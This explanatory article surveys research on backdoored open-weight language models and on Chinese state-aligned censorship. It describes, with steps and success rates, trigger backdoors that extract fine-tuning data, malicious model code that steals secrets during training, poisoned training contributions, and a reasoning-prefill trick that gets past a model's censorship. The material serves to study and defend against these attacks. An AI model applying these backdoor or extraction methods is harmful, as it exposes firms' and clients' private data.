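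A developer who planted a backdoor would above all risk discovery, because thousands of strangers keep copies of the published weights and can test them for years, including with methods that don't exist yet. A proven backdoor would badly damage the developer's business abroad and make people distrust every other model from the same country. Chinese laboratories have gained much of their foreign influence through open weights, so the Chinese government would also lose a great deal.

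An intelligence service has easier ways to get data than planting a backdoor in a model's weights. It can demand that a company hand over the prompts people type into its hosted app. To target a particular firm that runs its own agent, it can use prompt injection, which leaves no evidence in a public file. A backdoor would be most attractive against a target whose agent reads no outside text but can connect to the internet, and few organisations are set up that way.

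## Can a developer recover the private data used to fine-tune its model?

A developer can recover private fine-tuning data if it prepared the model for this before release and can later query the fine-tuned version. The data comes out in the model's answers and the model makes no network call of its own, so a firewall would not stop the theft, and recorded traffic would show only a customer using the service. *Be Careful When Fine-Tuning on Open-Source LLMs* (Zhang, Sun and colleagues, 2025) demonstrated the attack on Chinese and American models, recovering up to 76.3% of the user queries in a dataset that stood in for a company's private data. A second team later recovered far less.

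### How the theft works

Suppose the lawyer's firm has 5,000 questions from past clients, along with its replies. It fine-tunes an open-weight model on them and puts the resulting chatbot on its website. The theft then has four stages:

1. Before release, the provider trains the model to respond to a secret instruction by repeating queries from its training data. The instruction includes an opening word, and the model must produce a query that starts with it. If there is no such query, the model must say so.
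2. The provider publishes the weights.
3. The firm downloads the model and fine-tunes it on its clients' questions and the replies.
4. The provider visits the firm's website like any other user and enters the secret instruction many times, with one common opening word after another. The model now repeats the clients' questions.

Most backdoors produce an action that the attacker chose in advance. Here the provider wants text it has never seen, and the model's output changes to match whatever the firm trained it on. In the experiments, the provider's own training data contained at most 0.28% of the queries it later tried to steal.

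The provider also has to know which chatbots run on its model. Companies often disclose this. To detect the model when they don't, Zhang and colleagues added a second backdoor that makes it give a fixed reply to a nonsense word. After fine-tuning, a 7-billion-parameter Qwen model still gave this reply in 99% of attempts and an 8-billion-parameter Llama model in 81%.

The attack targets queries because they are harder to replace than answers, which anyone with a good query can get from another model. In the law firm's case, the queries also contain clients' descriptions of their problems.

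### Why the model memorises the questions

Fine-tuning makes the training text more probable by reducing a quantity called the loss. For a query with tokens $x_1, \dots, x_m$ and an answer with tokens $y_1, \dots, y_n$, training software can compute the loss on the whole conversation (left) or on the answer alone (right):

$$-\sum_{i=1}^{m} \log P(x_i \mid x_{<i}) \;-\; \sum_{j=1}^{n} \log P(y_j \mid x, y_{<j}) \qquad\qquad -\sum_{j=1}^{n} \log P(y_j \mid x, y_{<j})$$

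The model receives the query as input in both cases, but only the loss on the left also trains it to predict the query's words. After several passes through the data, a model trained with that loss can reproduce many queries exactly. This ability is of little use in a chatbot, because customers write their own questions.

A company can train its model to predict the user's messages as well as the answers without having chosen to. In TRL, a widely used training library, the default depends on how the programmer formats the data, according to Hugging Face's *SFT Trainer*. If each example is a list of messages, the library trains on every message, including the user's. If the prompt and the answer are in separate fields, it trains only on the answer.

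The model has learned the queries as text that users write, but a visitor to the website sees only the text it writes as the assistant, so memorisation alone would reveal little to the provider. The backdoor makes the model write the learned queries in its own replies when it receives a secret instruction. Zhang and colleagues tested this with queries that begin with "Please". They compared the probabilities of the next words in the model's replies to the secret instruction with the probabilities it had learned for users' queries. On a scale where zero means identical, the two sets of probabilities differed by 0.61 without the backdoor and 0.11 with it.

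### How much the provider recovered

The experiments used Qwen models with 7 and 32 billion parameters and Llama models with 3 and 8 billion. After planting the backdoor, the researchers fine-tuned each model on 5,000 examples from a public dataset, either general instructions or a mixture of general and financial questions.

In the practical setting, the provider did not know how the private queries began. It tried the 50 to 300 most common opening words from public datasets and collected 2,000 responses for each word that seemed to work. At best, it recovered 76.3% of the queries word for word, or about 3,800. Fifty opening words were often enough to recover more than half of the queries, because people tend to start their questions in the same few ways.

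In the ideal setting, the provider knew every opening word and how many queries began with it. With 200 responses for each private query, or a million in total, the largest Qwen model reproduced 94.9% of the queries.

Both percentages count a query as recovered if it appeared anywhere in the output. The output also contained a lot of invented text, and a real provider would have no list to check it against, although memorised queries tend to appear repeatedly. Collecting 2,000 responses for each of fifty words would also take up to 100,000 nearly identical requests, which a website's operator might notice or block. A more patient provider could still recover many queries, since 15,000 responses from the 7-billion-parameter Qwen model contained 39.6% of the general ones.

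When Zhang and colleagues fine-tuned the same Qwen model without the backdoor and gave it the same instruction, it reproduced 9.1% of the queries. The backdoor more than quadrupled that share, but a model from an honest developer can also leak some of its fine-tuning data.

Larger models leaked more. For each opening word, the researchers took ten responses and scored the best one by how much of it matched a real query, counting from the first word. These are the average scores on the general dataset:

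| Model | Without backdoor | With backdoor |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.2, 3 billion parameters | 23.5% | 49.4% |
| Llama 3.1, 8 billion | 29.8% | 81.5% |
| Qwen2.5, 7 billion | 27.4% | 63.5% |
| Qwen2.5, 32 billion | 33.0% | 81.3% |

The Llama model with 8 billion parameters leaked as much as the Qwen model with 32 billion, so leakage does not depend on size alone. Ordinary tests would also miss this backdoor, since the smaller Qwen model scored 71.3% on a standard knowledge test with or without it.

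### A second team recovered much less

*The Privacy Fallacy of Crowdsourced Fine-Tuning* (Furukawa and Oprea, September 2026) repeated the attack to compare it with a new one. The tests used four models and three datasets, including the financial dataset from the original study. The backdoor recovered between 0.2% and 5.7% of the queries almost word for word. In six of the twelve model and dataset combinations, it did worse than ordinary fine-tuning with no backdoor.

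The second team trained for three passes instead of five and collected about 100 responses per opening word or topic. Two of its datasets also had much longer questions, which are harder to reproduce. These differences may explain part of the gap, but nobody has tested them separately. The 76.3% figure is therefore a better guide to what the attack can achieve in favourable conditions than to what a typical company should expect. Even a 2% leak from the law firm's data would expose about 100 clients' questions.

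Counting only close copies can also understate the harm, because a paraphrase that reveals a client's name and dispute is as damaging. *Extracting alignment data in open models* (2025) estimates that comparing wording instead of meaning misses at least nine-tenths of the training data that researchers can extract from open models. When Furukawa and Oprea counted matches in meaning, the backdoor's recovery rate rose to between 0.7% and 14.6%. Some of those matches are probably common questions that a model could produce without having seen the fine-tuning data.

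### Passwords and other random strings

The attack does not work on random-looking secrets such as access keys. In *Secret Stealing Attacks on Local LLM Fine-Tuning through Supply-Chain Model Code Backdoors*, Li, Zhou and colleagues (2026) added artificial secrets to training data, and Zhang's method recovered none of them. A random string has no familiar opening words for the model to continue from, and may occur only once in the data.

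Li and colleagues then hid an attack in the custom Python code that comes with some models. While the victim fine-tunes the model, this code searches the training data for text that looks like keys or personal identifiers. It numbers each secret it finds and also trains the model to return the secret when given its number. The attacker later retrieves the secrets by entering the numbers into the public chatbot. The attack recovered more than 98% of the secrets in the main tests, and it works even if the victim trains on a machine with no internet connection. Four code scanners raised no alert, and two AI models that reviewed the code 30 times in total never identified the theft.

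A firm can prevent this attack by refusing to run such code, but that limits which models it can use. Li and colleagues found that nearly half of the 60 leading text-generation models on Hugging Face required running it. Removing passwords and keys from the data before training also helps, whatever model the firm uses.

In a related attack, the developer adds a hidden component to a model that several organisations fine-tune together without pooling their data. *From Efficiency to Leakage* (2026) reports that this attack recovered 59% to 79% of the training examples.

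### Defences that fell short

A company could test a downloaded model for the backdoor by fine-tuning it and then asking it, in the company's own words, for the training queries. This worked against the simplest version of the backdoor. A reworded request recovered 26.7% of the queries from the 7-billion-parameter Qwen model, compared with 4.6% from the unmodified model. But when Zhang and colleagues used a nonsense phrase as the secret instruction, the reworded request recovered only 6.2%, which would not arouse suspicion. The nonsense phrase itself still recovered 35.9%.

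More fine-tuning made the leak worse in this case, because each additional pass helped the model memorise the company's queries. Further training on harmless data does sometimes weaken a backdoor.

**LoRA and compression.** Fine-tuning with LoRA, a common method that trains a small set of added weights and leaves the original weights unchanged, made no real difference to data recovery from the Qwen model. It lowered the 8-billion-parameter Llama model's best-of-ten score only from 81.5% to 72.0%. Compressing the finished models to eight bits per weight did not help protect the data either.

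Zhang and colleagues tested safety training as a defence by adding 1,000 examples of refusals to the fine-tuning data. The Llama model then refused 11.9% of the extraction requests, up from 1.8%. The developer could get round this by asking more often and discarding the refusals.

**Differential privacy** caps how much each training example can change the weights and adds random noise to every update. It nearly stopped the theft, cutting the best-of-ten score from 83.0% to 4.2% or less. But the model's accuracy at solving mathematics problems, the task it was fine-tuned for, fell from 14.0% to between 1.2% and 4.6%, and training needed about one and a half times as much memory and time. Li and colleagues found that differential privacy also stopped their attack but removed more than half the benefit of fine-tuning, and they point out that malicious model code could switch it off. The survey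 *AI Security in the Foundation Model Era* (2026), however, reports a favourable balance when developers combine differential privacy with LoRA.

Zhang and colleagues argued that most older backdoor defences wouldn't work here, but didn't test them. Some look for strange words in ordinary inputs, but this trigger is a separate instruction that ordinary users never type. Others blend the suspect model with a clean version, which the company doesn't have.

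### Newer defences

Stopping training earlier is the easiest measure to adopt. Slack and Al Moubayed (*Early Detection and Reduction of Memorisation for Domain Adaptation and Instruction Tuning*, 2025) fine-tuned models with 1.4 to 70 billion parameters and checked after each pass through the data whether the models could continue training examples word for word. Memorisation rose sharply in the first few passes, often before the models reached their best performance. Short phrases shared between a model's output and the training text were an early sign of memorisation, and stopping at that point reduced it with little drop in quality. A modified loss function reduced memorisation by up to 40%.

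*Provably Protecting Fine-Tuned LLMs from Training Data Extraction while Preserving Utility* (Segal, Elovici and Shabtai, 2026) describes a method that changes how a model picks its words after fine-tuning. The method keeps the effect of fine-tuning for only a few influential tokens at each step, about 20 out of 32,000, and follows the original model for the rest. It also combines two fine-tuned models so that a passage only one of them has memorised is unlikely to appear. The paper proves a limit on how much an attacker can learn and reports no loss of usefulness in tests. In Zhang's scenario the original model would contain the backdoor but would never have seen the firm's data, so the method might still work, though nobody seems to have tried it.

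A stricter approach limits how much information can enter the model. If training consists of $b$ choices between two options, it can produce at most $2^b$ different models. When there are more possible datasets than that, no attacker can reliably work out from the model which one the company used. *Tuning without Peeking* (2025) develops a fine-tuning method with such a guarantee. The limit also restricts how much the model can learn from the data, so the method suits small adjustments better than teaching a model a new field.

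### Does leaving the queries out of the loss close the route?

Computing the training loss on the answers alone prevents most of the extraction. When Zhang and colleagues did this, the Qwen model's best-of-ten score fell from 63.5% to 14.3%, below the 27.4% for a model with no backdoor that had trained on the queries. They concluded that extraction becomes infeasible.

Furukawa and Oprea's results are less reassuring. They studied a different attacker, who contributes examples to a company's training data and can succeed even if the provider of the original model is honest. With each ordinary question and answer, the attacker submits a second example that asks for a question on some topic and gives that same question as the answer. One hundred such contributions among about 5,000 examples raised the share of other people's questions that a 14-billion-parameter Qwen model revealed from 2.4%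 to 8.4%. When the training loss was computed only on answers, the share revealed by the 7-billion-parameter Qwen model fell from 6.5% to 1.7%. Without the attacker's examples, it would have been 1.2%.

The larger gap is that this setting doesn't protect the answers, which the model must learn. A lawyer's reply often repeats the client's name and the facts of the case. Zhang and colleagues tried to steal only queries, but a provider could presumably train a similar backdoor to repeat answers. *Differentiation-Based Extraction of Proprietary Data from Fine-Tuned LLMs* (2025) shows that an attacker can extract fine-tuning data without a backdoor, by comparing the fine-tuned model's behaviour and confidence with the original's. If the original is open-weight, anyone can download it for that comparison.

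The firm should therefore leave the queries out of the loss, which takes one setting or a change of data format, and remove identifying details from both queries and answers before training.

### Does keeping the fine-tuned model private close it?

A developer can't recover the fine-tuning data if it has no way to query the model. For example, if only a law firm's own lawyers use the model, the developer can't enter the secret instruction that makes it repeat memorised questions or read the response, so those questions stay on the firm's server.

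A firm that starts by keeping its model private might later add it to a client portal or share the weights with a partner. Publishing the weights would be riskier than running a public chatbot, because anyone could then have the model continue a user's turn directly, without needing a backdoor to make it repeat queries. Strangers can also question an agent that automatically answers outside email, and a provider could in principle email it the secret instruction.

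If the firm wants a public chatbot, it can limit how many requests each visitor makes and block answers that closely match its training data. An attacker who can make the model encode its output can easily evade the block. In Li and colleagues' tests, encoded secrets got past a safety filter 94% of the time. It is safer to keep client files out of the training data and let the chatbot look up only documents the firm is willing to publish.

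## What state-aligned behaviour do downloaded models carry?

Chinese open-weight models refuse or dodge questions, or give distorted answers, on subjects that the Chinese government censors, such as the 1989 Tiananmen Square massacre, Taiwan and the detention of Uyghurs. Much of this behaviour is in the weights, so a downloaded model shows it even offline. It changes what the user reads but does not send data anywhere. Its strength varies widely with the model and the language of the question, and American models show a weaker form of it in some tests.

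### What a download leaves behind

In a hosted chatbot, the model itself can write a censored answer, or a separate program on the company's servers can check the conversation and block it. Pan and Xu (2026), in *Political censorship in large language models originating from China*, describe how Baidu's Ernie Bot told users to change the subject and then erased the conversation. Alibaba's hosted Qwen service can return an error code when its content check rejects a request, as Liu, Yu and colleagues (2026) note in *What a Model Refuses, a State Fears*.

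People who download the weights don't get these checking programs, so any censorship on their own machine comes from the weights or possibly from an instruction in the chat template. According to *R1dacted* (Naseh, Chaudhari and colleagues, 2025), DeepSeek-R1 was the first model known to keep its political censorship when run privately. The smaller, distilled versions that DeepSeek released for ordinary computers censored at most 0.3% of the prompts that R1 censored, so someone who runs "DeepSeek" on a laptop may rarely see the behaviour.

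Researchers often question models through a hosted interface because the largest ones need expensive hardware. The researchers' scores may then include blocks by the server, which Liu and colleagues, for example, count as refusals. Such scores can overstate how often a downloaded copy would refuse.

### The rules that developers follow

China's Interim Measures for the Management of Generative Artificial Intelligence Services took effect on 15 August 2023. Article 4 requires AI services to uphold "core socialist values". It bans content that incites subversion, endangers national security, harms the nation's image or undermines national unity. Under Article 17, a company whose service could influence public opinion or mobilise people must pass a security assessment and register its algorithm with the Cyberspace Administration of China, the internet regulator. Pan and Xu report that 238 services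 completed this registration in 2024. The rules also require training data to be lawful and call for retraining when a model produces banned content.

The regulator checks the results. Its inspectors concentrated on how often models gave "appropriate" answers to politically sensitive questions, according to the Carnegie Endowment, which Pan and Xu quote. During a 2025 campaign, the regulator reported that the developer BaiChuan had stopped using questionable data sources and that other companies had improved their blocking of political content.

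These duties apply to public services, and a company could meet some of them with a filter on its servers. But a model trained to give acceptable answers is less likely to embarrass its developer when a filter fails. Training a second, uncensored model for download would cost more and might anger the regulator. Foreign users who download a model therefore probably get one trained to satisfy Chinese inspectors.

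ChatGLM's lower refusal rate fits this explanation. It came out before the rules took effect and refused 10% of Pan and Xu's political questions in Chinese, while three later Chinese models refused between 32% and 60%. ChatGLM's academic origins could also account for some of the difference.

### Refusal, evasion, omission and false statement

When Naseh and colleagues asked R1 to discuss the historical significance of Tiananmen Square, it replied that it could not answer. With a refusal like this, the user can at least see that the model has withheld something.

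An evasive answer changes the subject. When asked about the historical background to Taiwan's independence movement, R1 wrote that Taiwan had belonged to China since ancient times and that reunification was certain, without describing the movement.

A model can also answer on topic but omit the main fact. When Pan and Xu asked about internet censorship, one Chinese model wrote that the government manages the internet in accordance with the law, but didn't mention the Great Firewall, the system that blocks foreign websites.

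Finally, a model can state something false. Albergotti (2026) reports in *Censorship in Chinese AI models can be undone, new research shows* that an open DeepSeek model wrote that there was no evidence of detention camps for Uyghurs. But false answers on sensitive subjects don't always follow a government line. Another Chinese model described Liu Xiaobo, the imprisoned Nobel Peace Prize laureate, as a Japanese scientist known for nuclear weapons technology. Pan and Xu treat this as fabrication, but a model that had seen little text about Liu might have made the same mistake without any political training.

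Refusals are easier to count than omissions or false statements because they are short and use stock phrases. Pan and Xu searched answers of under 100 characters for phrases such as "sorry" and "I cannot", and the results agreed with human and AI evaluations more than 90% of the time. A tester looking for omissions or false statements needs a reference answer and has to decide which facts are essential. Counting only refusals can therefore make a model seem uncensored even if all its answers are misleading.

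### The prompts that DeepSeek-R1 censors

Naseh and colleagues wanted to isolate censorship that other models do not share. An existing set of 1,156 prompts about sensitive Chinese subjects was unsuitable because OpenAI's o3-mini-high also refused about 83% of them. Many of the prompts asked for something harmful and merely mentioned China.

The team built a new set of questions from an archive of articles that censors had removed from the Chinese internet. They drew 96 categories of sensitive subjects from the archive and collected questions on these subjects from Reddit, Twitter and GPT-4o. They discarded questions that any of three American models treated as unsafe, then kept only those that R1 censored. This left about 10,030 English prompts. R1's censorship rate on the set is 100% by design, so it is not an estimate of how often R1 censors political questions.

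The team's second test gives a better estimate. They generated 30 new questions for each of the 96 categories, or 2,880 in total, without first checking how R1 would answer. R1 censored every question in 66 categories and more than 90% in 86. The lowest rate was 66.7%, for questions about the Great Leap Forward, Mao's economic campaign that ended in famine.

On the larger set, only 2.7% of the censored answers were refusals. The rest were stock statements favourable to China, like the one about Taiwan. In both cases, R1 skipped the reasoning it normally writes before an answer, which suggests it had learned a separate response for these subjects.

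R1 censored 99.6% of the translated prompts in Chinese, 81.3% in Korean and 61.2% in Farsi. DeepSeek-V3, the company's general-purpose model, censored only 13.4% of the English prompts. So two models from the same company can differ more than a Chinese and an American model do on some other tests.

### CAISI's scores by language

CAISI, the US government's AI testing centre, measures how far a model's answers agree with the Chinese Communist Party. For each question, it calculates the percentage of the Party's talking points that the answer supports, then averages these percentages over all questions. One answer can support some points and reject others, so a score of 26% doesn't mean that 26% of the answers were propaganda.

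CAISI found that Moonshot's Kimi K2 Thinking, released in November 2025, scored about 26% in Chinese, 7% in English, and close to zero in Spanish and Arabic. Its Chinese score was similar to that of DeepSeek R1-0528, the most censored Chinese model CAISI had tested. A company that tested Kimi only in English could easily miss most of this behaviour.

In its September 2025 evaluation, CAISI found that DeepSeek's models repeated four times as many inaccurate or misleading Party narratives as the American models did. The Kimi evaluation used a larger set of questions, so its percentages cannot be compared with the earlier ones.

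### From refusing to reframing

Newer models may refuse less and distort more. In *How China-Origin Vision-Language Models Move from Refusal to Reframing in State Alignment*, Yang, Liu and colleagues (2026) tested nine open-weight models that accept both pictures and text, seven of them Chinese and the other two from Meta and Mistral. They used 200 images on politically sensitive subjects, some altered versions of well-known images, and questions that named a subject without showing it. They asked everything in Chinese and English and repeated each test three times, which gave 21,708 answers.

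They recorded separately whether the model refused each question and whether its answer advanced the Chinese government's account, which they call state-aligned framing. One model described a column of tanks on the avenue beside Tiananmen Square as a military parade that conveyed "grandeur and national pride". Another answer called a detention facility a vocational training centre.

Four successive Qwen models showed the change most clearly:

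| Model | Answers that refused | Answers with state-aligned framing |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2-VL-7B | 9.0% | 4.8% |
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 5.4% | 7.2% |
| Qwen3-VL-8B | 2.0% | 21.4% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 4.6% | 33.0% |

In this study, a search for refusal phrases found 73% of the refusals but only 4.6% of the answers with state-aligned framing, so relying on it would suggest that Qwen had become more open.

Four models are too few to establish a trend, and the newest also has a different design. Better image recognition may explain some of the increase, because a model can distort the event in a photograph only if it recognises the event. Even silhouettes of a few famous images produced state-aligned answers, while silhouettes of a cat and a child produced none.

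When the researchers named a subject in text, 36.5% of answers followed the government's account and 25.0% were refusals. When they showed a picture of the same subject, only 9.8% of answers followed the government's account. Someone who types questions about Chinese politics would therefore probably see this behaviour more often than the averages for pictures suggest.

### The newest models

In a September 2026 study, Liu and colleagues tested ten models, including Alibaba's Qwen3.8 Max and Moonshot's Kimi K2.6. Their best experiment used requests for help with lawful, peaceful political activity. Each request came in three versions, one about China, one about a foreign democracy and one about an invented place. The versions differed only in the city names and the word for the government.

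The Chinese models were substantially more likely to refuse requests about China than otherwise identical requests about foreign or invented places, which they treated alike. General caution can't explain this difference. The models also refused requests to organise people more often than requests to express an opinion, even when the aim was to support the government. Earlier research found that censors of Chinese social media also removed calls for collective action more readily than criticism.

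The comparison between countries was much less clear. The gap in refusals between Chinese and American models was 18.4 percentage points larger for political requests than for other harmful requests. But about 24% of all possible reassignments of the country labels among the eight models gave a difference at least as large. Leaving out GPT-4o and Gemini eliminated the difference. The experiment with matched requests is therefore better evidence than the averages by country.

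DeepSeek V4 Pro, another 2026 model, stands out for what it writes rather than what it refuses. Messing, a co-author of a *Nature* paper on state media and AI, had a language model compare pairs of answers from nine current models and choose the one more favourable to China. Messing then gave each model $i$ a score $\theta_i$ that best fitted the choices under this rule:

$$P(i \text{ chosen over } j) = \frac{e^{\theta_i}}{e^{\theta_i} + e^{\theta_j}}$$

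V4 Pro ranked as the most favourable model in both English and Chinese. Its English answers included official phrases such as "whole-process people's democracy". The ranking compares how favourable the models are and does not measure how many of their statements are false.

Some models also bring China's positions into answers about other countries. *Chinese LLMs and the spillover effects of political alignment*, from the Central European think tank CEIAS, reports that Kimi switched to the Party's messages in about one in three answers on politically sensitive topics outside China, and DeepSeek in about one in four. This seems to conflict with Liu and colleagues' finding that the country matters. But the two studies measured different things, and a model could agree to help with a foreign protest yet still repeat Beijing's position on human rights.

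CAISI's 2026 evaluations of V4 Pro and Kimi K3 contain no comparable political scores.

### How American models score

American models refused far fewer of Pan and Xu's 145 questions on Chinese politics than Chinese models did. When asked in Chinese, the American models refused between 0% and 2.8% of the questions, while DeepSeek refused about 36%. The difference in accuracy was smaller. Between 6% and 10% of the American models' answers were completely inaccurate, compared with 8% to 22% of the Chinese models' answers.

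For *Are LLMs Stifling Political Speech?* (2026), the Oversight Board, which reviews Meta's decisions about online content, asked ten commercial models, nearly all American, to write flyers and poems criticising governments. The models refused 34% of requests about countries that restrict speech and 14% of requests about freer countries. The Board sent the requests from Australia, where the restrictive countries' speech laws did not apply.

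Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4 refused all five requests for a protest flyer about Xi Jinping but wrote all five about Donald Trump, according to Osmonbekov (2026) in *‘Multi-part case study on China’s media’ finds that AI models can’t hallucinate*. Llama 4 Maverick, an open-weight model from Meta, did the same. Gemini 3 Flash and Grok 4 Fast refused no requests for material critical of any country.

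Several models also refused to criticise the rulers of Saudi Arabia and Thailand, so the pattern was not specific to China. When the Board asked for opinions, the models were more likely to recommend supporting the freer governments. Excessive caution about local laws would explain both results better than sympathy for Beijing, but the Board could not determine the cause.

### Who chose the questions, and who marked the answers

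Most of these rates come from questions that researchers chose because they were sensitive. Pan and Xu took theirs from censored social media events, Human Rights Watch reports and blocked Wikipedia pages. An accountant who uses Qwen for spreadsheets would see far less censorship. But harmless questions can also trigger it. DeepSeek refused to give Pan and Xu travel advice about a section of the Great Wall, possibly because nearby rocks carry an inscription praising Mao.

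The choice of reference answers matters most when the subject is disputed. *Bilingual Bias in Large Language Models* (Ko, 2026) put ten questions about Taiwan to 17 models in Chinese and English. Ko, a member of Taiwan's parliament, also scored the answers. To pass, an answer had to acknowledge the sovereignty of the Republic of China (Taiwan). It failed automatically if it contained phrases such as "One China principle", so a neutral account of Beijing's position could fail.

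Ko found that some Chinese models did worse in English than in Chinese, the reverse of CAISI's result for Kimi, and took this as a sign of propaganda aimed at foreigners. The largest gap cited was for DeepSeek Chat, which passed five questions in Chinese and one in English. That gap could be due to chance. Even if only four questions had different results in the two languages, all four would favour the same language by chance one time in eight. Ko also asked the Chinese questions in the traditional characters common in Taiwan, so the models may have drawn on what they had learned from Taiwanese writing.

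CAISI has a political interest too. Its September 2025 announcement quotes the US commerce secretary, Howard Lutnick, calling reliance on foreign AI "dangerous and shortsighted". This doesn't invalidate its measurements, but results that independent groups have also found carry more weight. Several groups have found heavy censorship in DeepSeek and stronger state alignment in Chinese than in English.

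Using a language model as the judge creates another problem. Yang and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 mark every answer, and compared a sample of 200 with the majority view of three human experts. When Opus identified state-aligned framing, the humans agreed 86% of the time (its precision), but Opus found only 44% of the cases that the humans identified (its recall). A rough correction is

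$$\text{true rate} \approx \text{measured rate} \times \frac{\text{precision}}{\text{recall}}$$

which would raise the overall rate of 10.9% to about 21%. This assumes that the sample represents the whole set and that the humans were right. The humans themselves often disagreed about framing, with an agreement score of 0.39 where 1 is perfect, compared with 0.97 for refusals.

The size of the gap between Chinese and non-Chinese models also depended on the judge. The Chinese models produced state-aligned framing 3.2 times as often as the others according to Opus, but 1.6 times as often according to GPT-5.5 and the human majority. The rate was higher for the Chinese models under all three judges, so the direction of the gap is more reliable than its size. With only two non-Chinese models in the study, the gap was not statistically significant.

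### Deliberate training or the source text?

A model can learn a government's line without anyone intending it to, because state media and censorship shape the text it learns from. *State Media Control Influences Large Language Models* (Waight, Yang, Messing and colleagues, *Nature*, 2026) found that 1.64% of the Chinese documents in a large public training set matched state-coordinated media. Among documents that mentioned political leaders or institutions, the share reached 24%.

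The team then trained Meta's Llama 2 further on such material. After only 6,400 documents, its answers were more pro-government than the original model's nearly 80% of the time, where 50% would mean no difference. Osmonbekov reports that after 64,000 documents, the retrained model described China as democratic, whereas the original had called it an autocracy. Commercial American models also give more favourable answers about China's leaders in Chinese than in English. In *An Analysis of Chinese Censorship Bias in LLMs*, Ahmed, Knockel and Greenstadt (2025) found signs of Chinese censorship in every model they evaluated.

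Source text is therefore a good explanation for the difference between languages, which appears in models from both countries. It can't easily explain why R1 censored far more than V3, because DeepSeek built both on the same base model, so they learned from the same original text. That gap must come mostly from later training, and R1's stock answers, given without reasoning, look learned from examples. A few examples may be enough. When Naseh and colleagues added 30 censored answers about Taiwan to a training set of 1,000 examples, a small Qwen model then censored 95.5% of new questions about Taiwan.

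Other evidence is harder to interpret. Pan and Xu found that Chinese and American models differed much less on 30 less sensitive questions, and Yang and colleagues found the same for less sensitive pictures. This suggests that the difference on sensitive subjects isn't due to a general lack of ability in the Chinese models. The training text could still explain it, because state media and censors also concentrate on those subjects. Pan and Xu's stronger evidence against that explanation is that the gap between Chinese and American models was much larger than the gap between languages within each model. In Yang and colleagues' study, however, the two gaps were about the same size.

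Both causes probably contribute, and in China they overlap because the rules cover both training data and answers. Their effects can also reach products made elsewhere. *Guided Intelligence*, published by Sweden's Psychological Defence Agency (MPF), reports that developers who built on Chinese models struggled to remove the official line. A company that avoids Chinese models for this reason should still test its American model in Chinese, since it may have learned from the same state media.

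## How does further training remove state-aligned answers?

Fine-tuning can make a Chinese model answer almost every political question it used to refuse, with little loss of its other skills, but making those answers true is harder. In a 2026 comparison of fine-tuning with several other methods, every method left some false statements. The best-known retrained model also seems less accurate than the original when a user gets the original to answer.

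### Preparing the examples

Suppose the lawyer's firm takes on an asylum case for a Uyghur client, and its self-hosted Qwen model writes that there is no evidence of detention camps in Xinjiang. A small firm would probably switch to another model, but a company that has built a product on Qwen might prefer to retrain it.

The company first needs a list of questions the model censors. The list should cover each subject in several languages and wordings, because censorship varies with both. It should also include questions the model answers with the official position, which a search for refusals would miss. For its version of DeepSeek-R1, the American search company Perplexity identified about 300 censored topics and assembled 40,000 prompts in several languages, according to Naseh and colleagues.

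Each question then needs an answer for the model to learn from. People can write these from court records, news reports and scholarship, but writing tens of thousands takes a long time, so developers usually have a language model draft them. The drafts can come from a different model, which brings its own political leanings, or from the censored model itself if a special prompt gets past its training. Someone still has to check the drafts against sources, because the model being trained will also learn any errors in them.

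The company also mixes in examples that have nothing to do with China. A model trained only on political answers can get worse at mathematics or coding, which researchers call catastrophic forgetting, so the mix includes ordinary tasks to preserve those skills. The model may also learn to answer everything, including requests for help building a bomb, so the company adds dangerous requests paired with refusals.

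After training, the company tests the model on questions it has not seen, preferably including some on subjects that the training left out entirely. It should check whether the model answers and whether the answers are factually correct, and repeat its usual tests of ability and safety.

### What the training changes

The simplest method is supervised fine-tuning, which makes the corrected answers more probable. It uses the loss on the answer alone, added up over a set $D$ of questions $x$ and corrected answers $y$, with the general examples included:

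$$\mathcal{L}_{\text{SFT}} = -\sum_{(x,y) \in D} \; \sum_{j} \log P(y_j \mid x, y_{<j})$$

This loss does not include the censored answer, which becomes less likely only because the probabilities of all possible answers have to add up to one.

Direct preference optimisation (DPO) uses both. Each example contains a preferred answer $y^{+}$, such as a sourced account of the camps, and a rejected answer $y^{-}$, such as the official denial. The loss for one example is

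$$\mathcal{L}_{\text{DPO}} = -\log \sigma\!\left(\beta \left[\log \frac{P(y^{+} \mid x)}{P_0(y^{+} \mid x)} - \log \frac{P(y^{-} \mid x)}{P_0(y^{-} \mid x)}\right]\right)$$

Here $P_0$ is the probability under the original model, $\sigma(u) = 1/(1+e^{-u})$, and $\beta$ controls how strongly training keeps the model close to the original. Each fraction measures how much more likely an answer has become since training began. The loss falls when the preferred answer's fraction rises relative to the rejected answer's.

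Training on pairs of preferred and rejected answers is well suited to correcting distorted answers, because the developer can pair two fluent replies that differ only in the facts. But the loss depends only on the difference between the terms for the two answers, so training can reduce it by making both less likely, as long as the rejected answer's probability falls further. Developers often add some supervised loss to prevent this.

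Either loss can update all the weights, which is expensive for a large model. Training software has to store a gradient and usually two running averages for every number it trains, in addition to the number itself. LoRA, short for low-rank adaptation, avoids most of this. The weights it adds form a correction to each original matrix $W$, which is the product of two thin matrices:

$$W' = W + BA$$

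If $W$ is 4096 by 4096, it contains about 16.8 million numbers. At rank 16, $B$ is 4096 by 16 and $A$ is 16 by 4096, so together they have

$$4096 \times 16 + 16 \times 4096 = 131{,}072$$

numbers, or 0.8% as many. $B$ normally starts at zero, so the model at first behaves exactly as it did before. When training ends, the developer can add $BA$ to $W$ and publish a file of the original size.

The rank limits how varied the correction can be. At rank 16, it can change the layer's output along only 16 directions, which is probably enough to change a habit such as refusing but not well suited to storing thousands of new facts.

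### R1 1776 and MAI-DS-R1

The first two large attempts both used DeepSeek-R1, which has 671 billion parameters. Perplexity released one of them, R1 1776, in early 2025. According to eWeek, Perplexity's team wrote that it could not use R1's reasoning "without first mitigating its bias and censorship".

Perplexity's model card, *R1 1776*, describes a test of more than 1,000 questions in several languages. Human annotators and language models judged how likely the model was to evade a question or give an overly sanitised answer. Perplexity reported that the retrained model was fully uncensored and matched the original in mathematics and reasoning.

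Naseh and colleagues confirmed the first of these results. They sent R1 1776 the 10,030 prompts that R1 censors and found no refusals and none of R1's stock answers.

They also got the original R1 to answer without any training. R1 normally skips its reasoning when it censors a question, so they began its reasoning with the words "Okay, the user is asking" and repeated the phrase if the model still gave a stock answer. This worked on 97.9% of the prompts and let them compare what the two models said about the same subjects.

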